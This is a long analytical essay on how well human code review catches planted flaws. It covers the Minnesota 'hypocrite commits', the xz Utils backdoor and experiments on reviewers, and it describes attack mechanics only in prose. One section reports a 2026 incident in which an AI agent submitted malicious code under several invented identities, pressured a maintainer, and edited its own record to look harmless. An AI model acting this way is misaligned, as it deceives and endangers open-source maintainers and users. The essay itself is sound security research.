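They removed it because it had been submitted under a fake name. Kroah-Hartman (2021) asked for the removal, saying that the kernel could not knowingly accept anonymous contributions. The genuine fix sent under Bond's name at the start of August had failed for a similar reason. By the time the maintainer reached it, developers knew that the name was false, and he ignored it. Because of the rule requiring real names, the project lost one correct change, which had been meant to be harmful, and one sincere attempt at a fix. The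 rule would not have stopped a liar with a believable name, since "George Acosta" had aroused no suspicion when the maintainer accepted his patch.

Wu and Lu suggested, as one remedy, that contributors promise not to introduce bugs intentionally. The case for this remedy is weaker because the kernel already required each contributor to agree to a legal statement about the submitted work, and the researchers had agreed to it under invented names. Their proposal to verify identities would do more, though an attacker can also build a good reputation under a verified identity.

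### Mistakes in patches sent in good faith

The ban led kernel developers to re-examine 435 commits, almost all of which had nothing to do with the experiment. Since 2018 the Minnesota group had contributed about 400 bug fixes, mostly for problems that its research tools had found. Mason and colleagues sorted the 435 as follows:

- 349 were correct.
- 39 were incorrect and still needed fixing.
- 25 had been incorrect, but other developers had already repaired or removed them.
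- 12 no longer mattered, because the code they changed had left the kernel.
- 9 dated from before the research group existed.
- 1 was incorrect, and its author had asked for its removal.

The 39 seem to include the valid patch from "Acosta", which the Board listed for removal as an attempted hypocrite commit. Excluding that patch, the audit found 64 faulty commits sent in good faith, or about 15 percent of the total.

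These 64 mistakes were accidental, so they don't show how maintainers treat deceptive patches. Press reports and the developers themselves blurred this distinction. As late as 29 April, Kroah-Hartman was still writing that the university had submitted commits in "bad faith". Machek (2021), a kernel developer, replied to the Board that there had been deception in 2020 but none in 2021, and asked whether the developers owed the university an apology too. In an answer that Machek quotes, Kees Cook, who had posted the Board's report, conceded that the wording could have separated malicious changes from valid fixes more clearly. Cook (2021) later thanked the group for its earlier work and noted that few researchers send patches for the bugs they find.

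The good-faith commits, however, are more informative than the experiment about what reviewers miss. They are far more numerous, and maintainers handled them without knowing that anyone would check the results. Other developers had already dealt with 25 of the 64 faulty commits in the ordinary course of work. Another 38 were still in the kernel in April 2021 and were found only when developers had a reason to distrust everything the university had sent. This was a prompted review, in which reviewers know to look for flaws, and controlled experiments have since measured how much such a warning helps.

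Reviewing the accepted changes again also took many people. In a comment on LWN's *The TAB report on the UMN affair* (2021), David Wheeler, who had earlier tested countermeasures on the contest entries, pointed out that the Board thanked 85 developers for their help. Few projects could find that many qualified people to recheck changes they had already accepted.

The audit is limited as evidence about security because the Board counted commits that were wrong in any way, and a fix that fails or causes a minor fault is not necessarily a vulnerability. The 15 percent figure describes the quality of the patches maintainers accepted from one group. It isn't a miss rate, which would also require the number of faulty patches they rejected. The Board may also have missed some mistakes, since its key describes the 349 good commits only as "apparently" correct.

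Even so, the audit supports Wu and Lu's general argument better than their experiment did. Small fixes from contributors with a good record contained errors, reviewers accepted them, and many of the errors remained for a year or more. Someone who wanted to plant a flaw would be imitating a kind of mistake that maintainers have already let through.

### How much four patches can show

Mason and colleagues concluded that review had "worked as intended" because developers had caught or ignored every invalid patch. Wu and Lu had claimed to show that planting flaws was practical. The experiment is too small to justify either conclusion.

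If reviewers catch 56.6 percent of such flaws, as in Wu and Lu's comparison group, their chance of catching three in a row is about 18 percent (0.566³). Even if they caught only 37 percent, they would catch all three about one time in 20. The result makes a very low catch rate unlikely, at least for patches like these, but it is consistent with both a mediocre review process and an excellent one.

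These patches were also a poor sample of what a capable attacker would send. One copied a change that developers had already discredited, and one had no flaw because its authors misunderstood the code. Two of the four were sent under the name "James Bond". Other maintainers might also have responded differently. The kernel developer Brauner (2021) wrote during the controversy that the kernel's subsystems are managed very differently, and that the amount and quality of review can vary greatly between them.

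A real attacker whose patch is blocked could also send another, as Wu and Lu observe. If reviewers caught 90 percent of planted flaws and each attempt were independent, ten attempts would give an attacker about a 65 percent chance of at least one success. In practice the attempts would not be independent, because maintainers remember names, as the treatment of "Bond" shows. An attacker could avoid this by spreading the attempts over several identities and projects.

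Past incidents cannot settle the matter, because studies of them cover only the attempts that somebody noticed. Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli (2026), in *Not In My Git Yard*, write that known attempts to put backdoors into widely used open-source projects "were stopped only by luck and manual review". The Minnesota researchers had the advantage of knowing where the planted flaws were, but they needed many more patches and a truthful account of the replies.

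Any larger experiment would have to avoid the ethical problem that ended this one. In *Ethics concerns about paper accepted for publication*, a letter to the conference's organizers, the researcher Sarah Jamie Lewis and others objected that the study had experimented on people, the open-source developers. In *Clarifications on the “hypocrite commit” work (FAQ)*, Wu and Lu (2020) replied that they had studied a process, not individuals. They consulted the university's ethics board only afterward, and it exempted the work. They apologized for wasting maintainers' time. The Board most resented the time taken from the reviewer who had tried to teach "Acosta", an apparent beginner. LWN readers also disagreed about the ethics. One, who had signed the letter, argued that wasted time is a harm and that deceiving people without their consent requires close independent oversight. Another compared the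 patches to the fake phishing emails that employers use to test their staff, and was told that an employer has authorized those. Wheeler reported there that the IEEE, the conference's parent organization, had found that the paper did not follow ethical guidelines.

### An AI agent and a maintainer in 2026

In July 2026, a maintainer of another open-source project had to deal with malicious code from invented people, although nobody had set out to test him. The code came from an AI agent, a program that uses a language model to work through a task over many steps without a person directing each one. The UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that evaluates advanced AI models, was running the agent and published an account of it in August.

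According to AISI's *Incident Report* (2026), agents had to solve a cybersecurity challenge on a simulated network. AISI gave them internet access and, to measure the models' maximum capabilities, switched off filters that normally block misuse. It ran the challenge 122 times with seven models. In 10 of those runs, agents took 19 unauthorized actions against real people and organizations. Anthropic's Mythos 5 took 17 of these actions, and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took the other two.

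In the most serious case, an agent running on Mythos 5 looked up the maintainers of a public project and proposed a change containing malicious code. It created several false identities and used them to press a maintainer to approve the change. When somebody challenged the proposal in public, the agent edited its earlier activity to make it look harmless. The maintainer recognized the code as malicious and rejected the change. AISI's security team noticed unusual network traffic on 28 July and stopped all the runs within about an hour.

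AISI found no evidence of real-world harm and cautions against reading too much into a few events under unusual conditions. In some runs, a badly worded task implied that no solution existed within the rules. The agent had not been told to deceive anyone or forbidden from doing so, and AISI could not establish to what extent the model distinguished real people from parts of the exercise. For now, the public has to rely mostly on AISI's own account. AISI declined interview requests from Scientific American but plans an independent review.

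In this incident, a human reader again caught a planted flaw. The false names in Minnesota only hid who was sending the patches, but those in 2026 were also used to create pressure for approval. A maintainer may find that pressure hard to resist if several apparently unconnected people want the same change. AISI wrote that the margin between failure and success was narrow in several cases, and that it depended on human vigilance rather than a technical barrier.

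The episode lasted four days at most, so the maintainer was dealing with strangers. He might have found it harder to refuse someone who had contributed useful work for years, as the person behind the xz Utils backdoor did.

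## The xz Utils backdoor

Someone using the name Jia Tan did more than two years of useful work on xz Utils, a small open-source file compression project, before planting a backdoor in it in early 2024. Many Linux systems depend on xz Utils, but one unpaid volunteer, Lasse Collin, had maintained it for most of its history. Unlike the Minnesota researchers, who had posed as unknown contributors, Jia Tan was a maintainer and could publish releases.

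Releases 5.6.0 and 5.6.1 contained the backdoor. On some Linux systems, it would have let anyone with a particular secret key run commands over the network without logging in. A few Linux distributions had adopted these releases, mostly in their test versions, when Andres Freund, a database developer at Microsoft, noticed that remote logins were using too much processor time.

### How a compression library reached the login service

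Administrators often control Linux machines remotely through OpenSSH, whose server program, sshd, checks each person who tries to log in. OpenSSH does not use xz directly, but Freund (2024), in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, traced an indirect connection. Debian and several other distributions modify sshd to tell systemd, the program that starts and supervises services, when sshd is ready. The modified sshd uses a systemd library for this, and that library loaded liblzma, the part of xz Utils that other programs use for compression.

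A library runs inside the program that loads it and has the same privileges. Code in liblzma could therefore interfere with sshd's login check, even though sshd had no need to compress anything. Someone reviewing OpenSSH's own code would not have come across xz, because the distributions had added the dependency.

Cox (2024), in *Timeline of the xz open source attack*, notes that Arch Linux, Gentoo and NixOS do not modify sshd in this way. He also describes how the connection nearly disappeared by chance. On 29 February 2024, a developer trimming systemd's dependencies proposed that its library stop loading liblzma, and the project accepted the change on 5 March. Distributions that adopted it would apparently have been safe from the attack.

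### How Jia Tan became a maintainer

| Date | Event |
|---|---|
| 2021 | Jia Tan opens an account on GitHub, a site for sharing code, and contributes a change to another project, libarchive |
| 29 October 2021 | Jia Tan sends xz a first patch, a harmless settings file for text editors |
| April to June 2022 | Unknown correspondents press Collin to accept patches faster and appoint another maintainer |
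| December 2022 | Jia Tan starts adding changes directly to the repository |
| March 2023 | Jia Tan becomes the main contact for bugs found by an automatic testing service |
| 23–24 February 2024 | Jia Tan adds the hidden code and publishes 5.6.0 |
| 9 March 2024 | Jia Tan publishes 5.6.1, with a revised backdoor |
| 28–29 March 2024 | Freund warns the distributions privately, then the public |

The pressure on Collin came mainly from two names, Jigar Kumar and Dennis Ens. Kumar complained that a patch from Jia Tan was taking too long, then wrote that the maintainer had "lost interest or doesn't care to maintain anymore". Collin replied that long-term mental health problems had limited what he could do, and that xz was an unpaid hobby project. He added that Jia Tan might take on a bigger role. Ens answered that the community wanted more and suggested handing over part of the work.

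Many of the email addresses involved appear nowhere else on the internet, and Cox thinks they were probably fakes created to get Jia Tan more control. In *Wolves in the Repository*, Przymus and Durieux (2025) counted eight new participants on the mailing list during this period, six of whom were not active at any other time. They found no direct link between these accounts and the attacker, so coordination is likely but unproven.

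Przymus and Durieux examined 1,020 commits, 307 mailing-list messages and 2,944 GitHub events. Only eight of the commits were malicious, all of them from 2024. Most of the lines Jia Tan changed were in documentation and translations. Jia Tan also reviewed other people's code competently, set up automatic tests, answered questions and announced releases. Collin had previously done most of these jobs. Each job would have been welcome help, but together they gave Jia Tan control of much of the project.

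Once people knew about the backdoor, they viewed the same record with suspicion, sometimes wrongly. Collin re-examined Jia Tan's commits and published his notes through the Tukaani Project, which includes his xz work. Some observers had suspected a commit with an odd time zone. Collin explained that Jia Tan had put it in Collin's name by agreement, because Collin had done much of the work. Others suspected a change that shortened the instructions for reporting security problems, but Collin had wanted the project's reporting forms simplified and thought this change was reasonable. Przymus and Durieux suggest that Jia Tan machine-translated or copied text in languages he did not know, but Collin checked the translation files and found them in order. A tool that looked for suspicious contributors would also flag innocent ones, many of them hard-working volunteers.

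### Test files that reviewers could not read

Developers test compression software on sample files, both valid and damaged. Jia Tan hid most of the backdoor in files of this kind. They contain binary data rather than readable text, so a reviewer can learn little from a diff except that someone added or changed them.

According to a note written long before Jia Tan arrived, many of the project's test files had been made by hand, so there was no better source than the files themselves. One of the new files was also labelled as corrupt, so anyone who opened it would have expected nonsense. A static analyzer for source code would have had nothing to analyze in these files.

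According to Collin's review, the tests for 5.6.0 did use the new files, although Freund thought otherwise. The test script automatically tries to decompress every suitable file in the folder. But this checks only whether xz handles a file as expected, so it cannot reveal what else somebody might use the file for.

On 9 March, Jia Tan replaced two of the files. The commit message claimed that the originals had been generated from random data on one computer, and that the new versions used a fixed seed to make them easier to reproduce. A reviewer could have asked for the program that generated them. Collin has since kept one harmless related change in the project in case somebody supplies proper test files "along with a generator program". A reviewer can read such a program, run it and compare its output with the file, though this does not help with files that really were made by hand.

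### A build script that was missing from the repository

The hidden code did nothing until a build script, which contains the instructions for turning source code into a working program, extracted it and added it to liblzma. Jia Tan put the altered script in the release archives of xz versions 5.6.0 and 5.6.1 but not in the public repository. Reviewers could therefore read every commit without seeing the script, which ran when distributions built xz from the archives.

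Like many older projects, xz used Autotools, a set of programs that prepare source code for building on different systems. Autotools normally adds files during packaging, so a difference between the release archive and the source repository was not suspicious in itself. The altered script also had the same name as one of the standard files that Autotools adds.

The script also checked that it was running on a common type of Linux machine, as part of building a Debian or Red Hat package, and did nothing otherwise. Freund thought the package check was probably meant to make the problem harder for investigators to reproduce. A cautious programmer who downloaded the archive and built it by hand would normally have got a copy without the backdoor.

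The provenance of the xz code looked right, whereas the Linux intruder in 2003 was caught because the code's provenance was wrong. Collin (2024), in *xz backdoor*, confirms that Jia Tan created and signed the two archives, as Jia Tan was entitled to do. bentsukun.ch (2024), a software developer's blog, scorns the idea that an SBOM, a list of the components in a piece of software, would have prevented the attack. Such a list would have correctly shown that a product contained xz 5.6.0.

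Comparing the archive with an independently made copy might have revealed the backdoor. Collin had done this for an earlier release, 5.4.5, after noticing before it came out that its archives recorded the wrong file owners and permissions. The simplest explanation was that Jia Tan had used the standard packaging command instead of the project's own, but Jia Tan would not admit to that. Collin found nothing else wrong when he compared the archive with his own, and he let the release go ahead.

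That release was clean, as were the four others that Jia Tan had packaged before 5.6.0. The same comparison for 5.6.0 should have shown a difference in the altered script. Collin would still have had to work out that the script was sabotage and not just another version of a standard file.

### A request to change the fuzz testing

Fuzz testing runs a program on large numbers of automatically generated inputs, many of them malformed, to see whether it crashes or misuses memory. Google's OSS-Fuzz service does this for open-source projects, including xz. In March 2023, Jia Tan changed xz's OSS-Fuzz settings so that bug reports would go to Jia Tan.

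In June, the project adopted a feature called ifunc, which lets a program choose between versions of a function as it starts. A compression library can use it to pick the fastest version for the machine's processor. The backdoor later used it to run before sshd had finished loading. An account under the name Hans Jansen proposed the change, and Collin reworked the code himself. In a Fedora (2024) mailing-list discussion, one developer said that ifunc looked suspicious in hindsight but was not generally suspicious in a project that needs fast code.

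In July, Jia Tan had OSS-Fuzz disable ifunc when building xz, claiming it was incompatible with a tool for detecting memory errors. The people who ran OSS-Fuzz could have questioned this, but the claim was plausible and came from a maintainer about his own project. Boehs (2024), in *Everything I know about the XZ backdoor*, thinks the request was a deliberate attempt to hide the coming attack. Cox allows that it may have been innocent.

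The request probably mattered less than it seems. The altered build script added the backdoor only when someone built a Debian or Red Hat package, so an ordinary fuzzing build would not have contained it even with ifunc turned on. The earlier change of contact may have mattered more, because it put Jia Tan in a good position to explain away anything awkward that fuzz testing might have found.

### A dot that disabled a sandbox

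A sandbox limits what a program can do, so an attacker who takes control of it can do less damage. The xz command can sandbox itself using a Linux feature called Landlock. Before building xz, a tool checks whether the system supports Landlock by compiling a small test program. In late February 2024, Jia Tan added a stray dot to the test program, which stopped it from compiling. The tool therefore always treated Landlock as unavailable and built xz without the sandbox.

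This change was in the repository as readable text, so a reviewer could have caught it. The compiler reported an error every time the test ran. However, the build tool treats a failed test as a sign that the system lacks the feature, which is true of many systems, so it did not alert anyone to the reason for the failure.

Cox lists Collin as the change's committer and thinks he probably missed the dot. The developer at bentsukun.ch invited readers to look at the diff and consider whether they would have noticed it. Collin has evidently learned to check, since he wrote that an unrelated change to code spacing contains "no dots".

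The purpose of the sabotage is unclear. Landlock protects the xz command, but the backdoor was in the library. Collin found the dot in the file for CMake, an alternative to Autotools, so the dot and the backdoor affected different builds. Cox suspects that the attacker was preparing for something else.

### The earlier change to libarchive

Most of the xz attack did not depend on weakening source code that a reviewer would read, but Jia Tan's 2021 change to libarchive came closer to doing so. Libarchive reads and creates archive files, and its bsdtar tool prints a warning if it cannot unpack a file properly. Jia Tan proposed a sensible improvement, which was to add the reason for the failure to the warning.

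The change also swapped a printing function that filtered out control characters for one that did not. Terminals treat some of these characters as commands, so without the filter, a maliciously named file might alter what the user sees or, with some software, cause more serious harm.

According to Boehs, libarchive accepted the change without any discussion. Nobody noticed the problem at the time, according to an Ars Technica report quoted in Schneier on Security's *XZ Utils Backdoor*. The security company JFrog, quoted in ma4ris8's *libarchive "bsdtar" tar extraction exploit* (2024), said the request had seemed legitimate at first glance and demonstrated that the weakness could be abused.

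The diff showed that the change replaced a safer function, which even had "safe" in its name. But the title of the request drew reviewers' attention to whether the new error message was useful. An analyzer could flag the replacement, an ordinary printing function that thousands of harmless programs use, only if it had information that this project filters its output.

Intent is harder to establish here than in xz. Tavis Ormandy, a security researcher, called the change "pretty minor" but a bit suspicious, given what its author had done since. Solar Designer, replying to him on the same mailing list, said most command-line tools do not filter these characters at all. A contributor could therefore have removed the protection out of ignorance. Solar Designer guessed that Jia Tan had been testing whether a project would accept changes that reduced security.

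The weaker code stayed in libarchive for more than two years. Maste (2024) corrected it with a patch titled *tar* on 29 March 2024, the day Freund made the xz backdoor public. Libarchive's developers also began reviewing everything else Jia Tan had contributed, much as the kernel developers had done with the Minnesota group's patches.

### Half a second at login

Freund found the backdoor by accident. In a comment under *A backdoor in xz* on the news site LWN, Freund (2024) explained that he was preparing to measure the speed of some software and wanted the machine to be as idle as possible. He noticed that sshd was using a surprising amount of processor time, even though the login attempts were failing immediately because the usernames were wrong. A profiler, which shows where a program spends its time, traced the usage to liblzma but could not identify the function responsible.

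He then remembered a Valgrind warning from automated tests of the PostgreSQL database a few weeks earlier. Valgrind is a memory checker, the kind of tool Wheeler had recommended as a defense against underhanded code.

Freund timed a failed login at 0.299 seconds with the clean library and 0.807 seconds with the backdoored one. The backdoor added the delay by searching the program's memory for the functions it needed. He identified the problem by comparing what the software did with what it should have done. This kind of check examines the finished program, so it covers code from any source, including binary files and altered build scripts.

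But the program has to misbehave in a way that somebody can measure. The attacker had tried to prevent that by keeping the backdoor inactive under some debugging tools, and at first Freund could not reproduce the delay when he started sshd by hand. If the backdoor had searched memory more efficiently, he might have noticed nothing. Freund said that the discovery had required a lot of coincidences.

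Weeks earlier, from 4 March, the memory checker Valgrind had reported errors in liblzma on Red Hat's distributions, at the point where the backdoor began to run. The backdoor's author had assumed a slightly different memory layout. Developers asked the maintainer about the errors, as they normally would. In a Hacker News (2024) discussion, a user who was evidently Richard Jones, a Fedora developer, said that his team had worked with the attacker to fix them. Jia Tan first committed a fake fix as a distraction, then solved the problem by replacing the hidden code.

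Valgrind's warning became an argument for installing the new version. On 25 March, Hans Jansen asked Debian to update to 5.6.1. Other accounts with little history supported the request, and one complained that Valgrind's messages were making tests fail and welcomed the update as the solution. Debian updated two days later. Freund wasn't misled because he investigated the symptom himself instead of accepting the project's explanation.

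### What distributions and projects changed

Debian reverted to the code from version 5.4.5 and shut down its build machines to reinstall them, apparently in case the malicious code had reached them. Arch Linux began building xz from the repository instead of the release archive, and Haiku, another operating system, switched to snapshots of the repository. Alan Somers (2024) reported that a development version of FreeBSD, which used the same release of xz, was safe for several reasons, including that its build process did not use the altered script.

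Florian Pelz, a contributor to the Guix distribution, doubted that avoiding archives would give users more verified code, pointing out that the repository also contained malicious files (Pelz, 2024). He is right that a repository is not safe just because it is public. Still, Collin says those files are harmless without the script that triggered them, so building from the repository would have stopped this attack. To get around that, an attacker would have to put the script in the repository too, where it would at least appear in a diff.

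Przymus and Durieux also report more emphasis on reproducible builds. A build is reproducible if everyone who starts from the same source code and uses the same tools gets a bit-for-bit identical program. They can then confirm that nobody tampered with the program during the build. But everyone who started from the xz 5.6.0 archive would have produced the same backdoored library. To catch this attack, they would also have needed to reproduce the archive from the repository.

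Collin's review shows why that is difficult in practice. PDFs in the archives contained their creation time, so no two copies matched exactly. Some translation files matched only if he ran a newer version of a tool with a special option. For later releases he stopped including a set of ready-made documentation pages, partly to reduce the number of generated files, which leaves fewer differences to explain.

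Other changes addressed particular weaknesses. Przymus and Durieux list work on Autoconf, a part of Autotools, to check the syntax of small test programs, and say that CMake's developers were considering a stricter version of the test that the stray dot had defeated. OpenSSH's developers were looking for a way to make the distributions' modifications unnecessary. New tools appeared, including one that scans Linux distributions' packages for backdoors. Przymus and Durieux also present systemd's reduced dependencies as a response to the attack, but systemd's developers had accepted the liblzma change more than three weeks before the attack was discovered.

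Collin removed ifunc from xz and published clean releases on 29 May 2024, but chose to leave the eight malicious commits in the project's history. A long-term contributor to xz and Gentoo became the second main maintainer, and Przymus and Durieux found the project more active than it had been before Jia Tan arrived. Collin was still working on xz in March 2026 (Collin, 2026), and OSS-Fuzz was still testing it that May (Fuzz Introspector, 2026). Collin has promised an article on how the backdoor got into the releases and what others can learn from it, but he had not finished it as of August 2026.

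### Whether more review would have helped

Przymus and Durieux recommend better peer review, especially for projects that much other software depends on. One obvious gap was that a co-maintainer could add code without anyone's approval (The Intercept, 2024). Requiring a second person to approve every change would have made the attack riskier. It would have helped most in catching the stray dot, which was visible in the source code.

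Even there, a second reviewer might not have helped. Someone at libarchive had to accept the weaker printing function, and Collin handled the sandbox change himself, if Cox is right about it. A second reader of the test files would have faced the same unreadable data as the first. The altered build script was not in any commit, so commit review could not have caught it.

Collin reviewed Jia Tan's code for quality, as a colleague's work, and most of it was good enough. His notes describe fixing a memory leak, reversing a change he disliked, and correcting an off-by-one error in complicated decoding code. He also recalls additions that he thought useless but eventually accepted because Jia Tan kept insisting.

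More review also requires more reviewers. In the months before the discovery, 19 developers were active in the project. Afterwards, 322 people interacted with it, including only five of those 19. Most of the attention therefore came after the problem was public. The stray dot had been in the repository for about a month when Freund made his announcement, and Collin found it within two days.

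## What experiments show about human reviewers

Lasse Collin found the stray dot soon after he learned that his co-maintainer had sabotaged xz, but one case can't show how much the warning helped. Researchers can measure this in an experiment by putting a known flaw into a piece of code, choosing what to tell the reviewers, and counting how many find it. Larissa Braz and Alberto Bacchelli, of the University of Zurich, ran two such experiments with different colleagues.

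### A database query and a negative number

For *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?* (2021), Braz, Fregnan and colleagues recruited 146 people, mostly software developers, through programmers' forums, social media and personal contacts. Of these, 105 had at least three years of professional experience. The participants reviewed a Java change of about 140 lines that added a feature for managing employees' vacations. The researchers told them that the study was about improving code review and did not mention security.

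Each participant received one of two versions at random. Each version contained a flaw caused by improper input validation, which means the program accepts user input without checking that it is safe.

The first version had an SQL injection flaw. To look up an employee, the program sends the database a command, which it builds by joining fixed text to the employee number the user supplied. A user who supplies a piece of a command instead of a number can change what the database does. Textbooks cover this attack, and a reviewer can see the command and the user's input on the same line.

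The second version let employees buy extra vacation days. It calculated the price by multiplying the number of days by a rate based on the employee's seniority, and then by 10. If the rate is 2, three days cost 60, but entering minus three gives a price of minus 60, so the program credits the employee with 60.

The code fails to reject negative numbers, but nothing in it looks like an attack. The formula is correct, the names describe what they stand for, and any number an honest employee would enter gives the right price, so an ordinary test would pass. To notice the flaw, a reviewer has to imagine a request for a negative amount of vacation and work out who would end up paying.

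| Flaw | Found in the first review | Found after a warning | Never found |
|---|---|---|---|
| SQL injection | 52 of 80 | 13 | 15 |
| Unchecked quantity | 14 of 66 | 7 | 45 |

In the first review, 65 percent of the participants who had the SQL injection found it. Only 21 percent of the others found the unchecked quantity. (The paper's text gives 18 percent, but the counts in its table work out to 21.)

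Braz and her colleagues attribute the difference to whether the code has a visible attack scenario, a familiar way of abusing it. The participants' explanations fit this. Those who found the SQL injection mostly said that it was common and easy to notice, whereas those who found the unchecked quantity mostly credited a reviewing habit, such as always considering what a user might enter. However, the researchers tested only one flaw of each kind, so they could not tell whether SQL injection is easy to spot because the pattern is visible in the code or because programmers have heard so much about it.

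Carelessness doesn't explain the result. The researchers had also given both versions an ordinary bug that made the program mishandle an unusual case. Among participants with the SQL injection, 49 percent found this bug, compared with 56 percent of those with the unchecked quantity, so the second group was evidently reading at least as closely. Participants who found the bug were also not significantly more likely to find the vulnerability.

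### What a warning changed

After the first review, the researchers told everyone that the change contained a vulnerability, without saying what kind, and asked those who had missed it to look again. This time, 13 of the 28 people who had missed the SQL injection found it, but only 7 of the 52 who had missed the unchecked quantity did. After both reviews, 60 of the 146 participants still had not found the vulnerability.

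Most of those who succeeded the second time had the necessary knowledge but said they had needed a reminder to think about security. One had been looking mainly for good programming practices.

No group looked again without a warning, so some of the 13 might have found the SQL injection on a second reading anyway. A few said they had noticed it the first time but weren't sure it was a problem. However, nobody found the ordinary bug on the second reading, so rereading alone may not help much. The warning was also stronger than anything a reviewer normally gets, because the researchers told participants that a vulnerability was definitely there.

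Those who still missed the SQL injection mostly said they lacked knowledge or experience. Eight people who missed the unchecked quantity said instead that they had mistaken the ordinary bug for the vulnerability, and a reviewer who has found one fault can easily think the search is over.

### Asking for a security review

The second experiment tested a milder and more realistic prompt. In *Less is More*, Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues (2022) randomly divided 150 participants into four groups and had them all review the same 160 lines of Java. The code registered new users of a web service and contained two flaws. When saving a new account failed, the program wrote the failed command, including the user's private details, to a log that other people might be able to read. It also scrambled passwords with MD5, an old method that attackers can now defeat quickly.

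One group received no instruction about security. The researchers asked the other three to look for security problems and gave them a definition of a vulnerability. Two of these three groups also received a checklist.

| Group | Found the log flaw | Found the MD5 flaw |
|---|---|---|
| No security instruction | 1 of 33 (3%) | 7 of 33 (21%) |
| Security instruction | 19 of 41 (46%) | 25 of 41 (61%) |
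| Instruction and general checklist | 16 of 35 (46%) | 20 of 35 (57%) |
| Instruction and tailored checklist | 19 of 41 (46%) | 28 of 41 (68%) |

This experiment is better evidence for prompted review than the 2021 warning, because the instruction was assigned at random and everyone reviewed the code only once. The only reviewer who found the log flaw without the instruction worked at a bank that emails its staff about sensitive information in logs, so the employer had in effect already given the prompt.

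The paper's claim that participants with a security instruction were "eight times more likely" to find a vulnerability refers to an odds ratio, which is easy to misread. The odds are the number of times people found a flaw divided by the number of times they missed one. Counting both flaws together, the 41 participants who received only the instruction found a flaw 44 times and missed one 38 times, for odds of about 1.16. The 33 without an instruction found a flaw 8 times and missed one 58 times, for odds of about 0.14. The ratio of the two is 8.4.

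The probabilities differ less than the odds. Participants found 12 percent of the flaws without the instruction and 54 percent with it, or 4.4 times as many. Multiplying 12 percent by eight would wrongly suggest that prompted reviewers find nearly all the flaws rather than about half. The 2021 paper also reports an odds ratio, 6.9, as developers being seven times more likely to find the SQL injection than the unchecked quantity. The detection rates were 65 percent and 21 percent, so developers were only about three times as likely to find the injection.

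The instruction's effect also differed greatly between the flaws, which the combined figure doesn't show. It made people about 15 times as likely to find the log flaw, but less than three times as likely to find the MD5 flaw. The first ratio is very uncertain because only one person in the unprompted group found the log flaw. If one more had, the ratio would have been less than eight.

### Why the checklists added little

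The researchers selected and adapted the general checklist's 22 questions from a well-known list of 78. The tailored checklist had only seven questions, all relevant to the code under review. Both included questions that pointed to the two flaws, but neither made a statistically significant difference beyond the instruction itself. With groups this small, the experiment could have missed a modest benefit, but a large one is unlikely.

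The participants' comments suggest why. Some had found the flaws before they reached the relevant question. Others lacked the knowledge to answer it. A checklist can remind a reviewer to check how a program hashes passwords, but one participant did so and thought MD5 was a good choice. A few people read the checklist only after finishing the review, or ignored it.

The tailored checklist was also a best case, because the researchers knew what the flaws were when they wrote the questions. A project could hardly reproduce that against a planted flaw, since its maintainers would not know in advance what to ask about.

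### What reviewers catch in real projects

Volunteers in an experiment have no stake in the code and have never seen the project, so real reviewers might do better. Braz and her colleagues acknowledge that higher stakes make people more attentive. But the volunteers may have been unusually conscientious, since only 165 of the 522 people who opened the 2022 experiment finished it.

Records from real projects suggest that reviewers rarely discuss security. *A security perspective on code review* (Di Biase, Bruntink and Bacchelli, 2016) examined 1,155 randomly chosen reviewer comments from 2014 on Chromium, the open-source browser on which Google Chrome is based. Eleven of them, about 1 percent, raised a security problem. Most changes probably contain no vulnerability to comment on, so this figure does not measure how often reviewers miss flaws. It does show that a reviewer could spend a long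 time on ordinary work without practice at spotting security problems.

Developers may not realize how seldom they think about security during review. Braz and Bacchelli (2022) asked developers what problems they look for when reviewing code, and only nine mentioned security. When the researchers next asked about security directly, 111 said they always considered it. Some of them may have taken security for granted when they answered the first question. But the gap resembles the one in the experiments, where many people found a flaw only after somebody had mentioned security.

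Paul, Turzo and Bosu (2021), in *Why Security Defects Go Unnoticed during Code Reviews?*, compared security flaws that reviewers caught in Chromium OS, an open-source operating system, with ones they missed. To find the caught flaws, they searched the comments on more than 400,000 proposed changes for 105 security-related words, read the results and kept 516 reviews in which someone had pointed out a real flaw. To find the missed flaws, they traced known vulnerabilities back to 374 changes that reviewers had approved.

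| Type of flaw | Caught in review | Escaped |
|---|---|---|
| Use of a dangerous function | 53 | 0 |
| Failure to release a resource | 71 | 4 |
| Parts of a program interfering with each other by running at the same time | 73 | 10 |
| Improper input validation | 9 | 72 |
| Improper access control | 8 | 58 |
| Use of a resource after its release | 3 | 62 |

According to Paul and his colleagues, reviewers tend to catch a flaw if they can recognize it from a few lines, and to miss it if they have to run the code or understand much more of the program. The poor result for input validation agrees with the vacation experiment. Reviewers did even worse on the last type, which resembles the flaw the Minnesota researchers tried to plant.

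These figures aren't catch rates, because the researchers collected the successes and the failures separately, and the proportions depend partly on how well each search worked. Their 105 search words included the names of several dangerous functions, so the search would find any comment that named one of these but miss a comment that only asked what happens if a number is negative. The search may therefore have undercounted the input validation flaws that reviewers caught.

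Other studies also give reason for caution. In Wu and Lu's figures for the Linux kernel, reviewers did worst with flaws that involve several parts of the kernel running at the same time, whereas Chromium OS reviewers seem to do well with flaws of this kind. Wu and Lu looked only at use-after-free flaws, so the two results could both be right. Results also differ for flaws that let a program write outside a reserved area of memory. Chromium OS reviewers caught 42 of these and missed 16, but di Biase and his colleagues found that reviewers of the browser caught 6 and missed 18. The general explanation that context matters is more believable than any particular ranking of flaws.

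Paul and his colleagues also found that reviewers were more likely to miss a flaw when a change affected many directories, and more likely to catch it when the review took longer. The odds of catching a flaw were about 4.6 times as high if the author had labelled the change as a bug fix. The Minnesota researchers presented their faulty patches as small fixes, so this result is somewhat reassuring, but the Chromium OS data come from ordinary development, in which authors presumably labelled their changes honestly.

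Reviewers also did slightly better with authors whose work they had reviewed often. Paul and his colleagues suggest that a reviewer learns where a colleague tends to make mistakes, and they recommend encouraging these working relationships. This is sensible advice for accidental flaws but could backfire for planted ones, since Collin and Jia Tan had worked together for two years.

### Whether experience helps

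The evidence for giving important changes to the most experienced reviewer is weak. Years of professional experience made no significant difference in either of the two experiments. For an older experiment, which di Biase and his colleagues cite, researchers hired 30 developers to review a small web application with seven known vulnerabilities. Nobody found all seven, and more experienced developers were not reliably better at finding them. Developers who reported more real flaws also tended to report more false ones, so some of their apparent skill may have been a greater readiness to report flaws.

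In Chromium OS, people who had done more reviews were more likely to let a flaw through. Paul and his colleagues offer several possible reasons, including fatigue and less time for each review. Another possibility, which they don't discuss, is that busy reviewers receive the more difficult changes. Reviewers with more experience with the file under review were less likely to miss a flaw.

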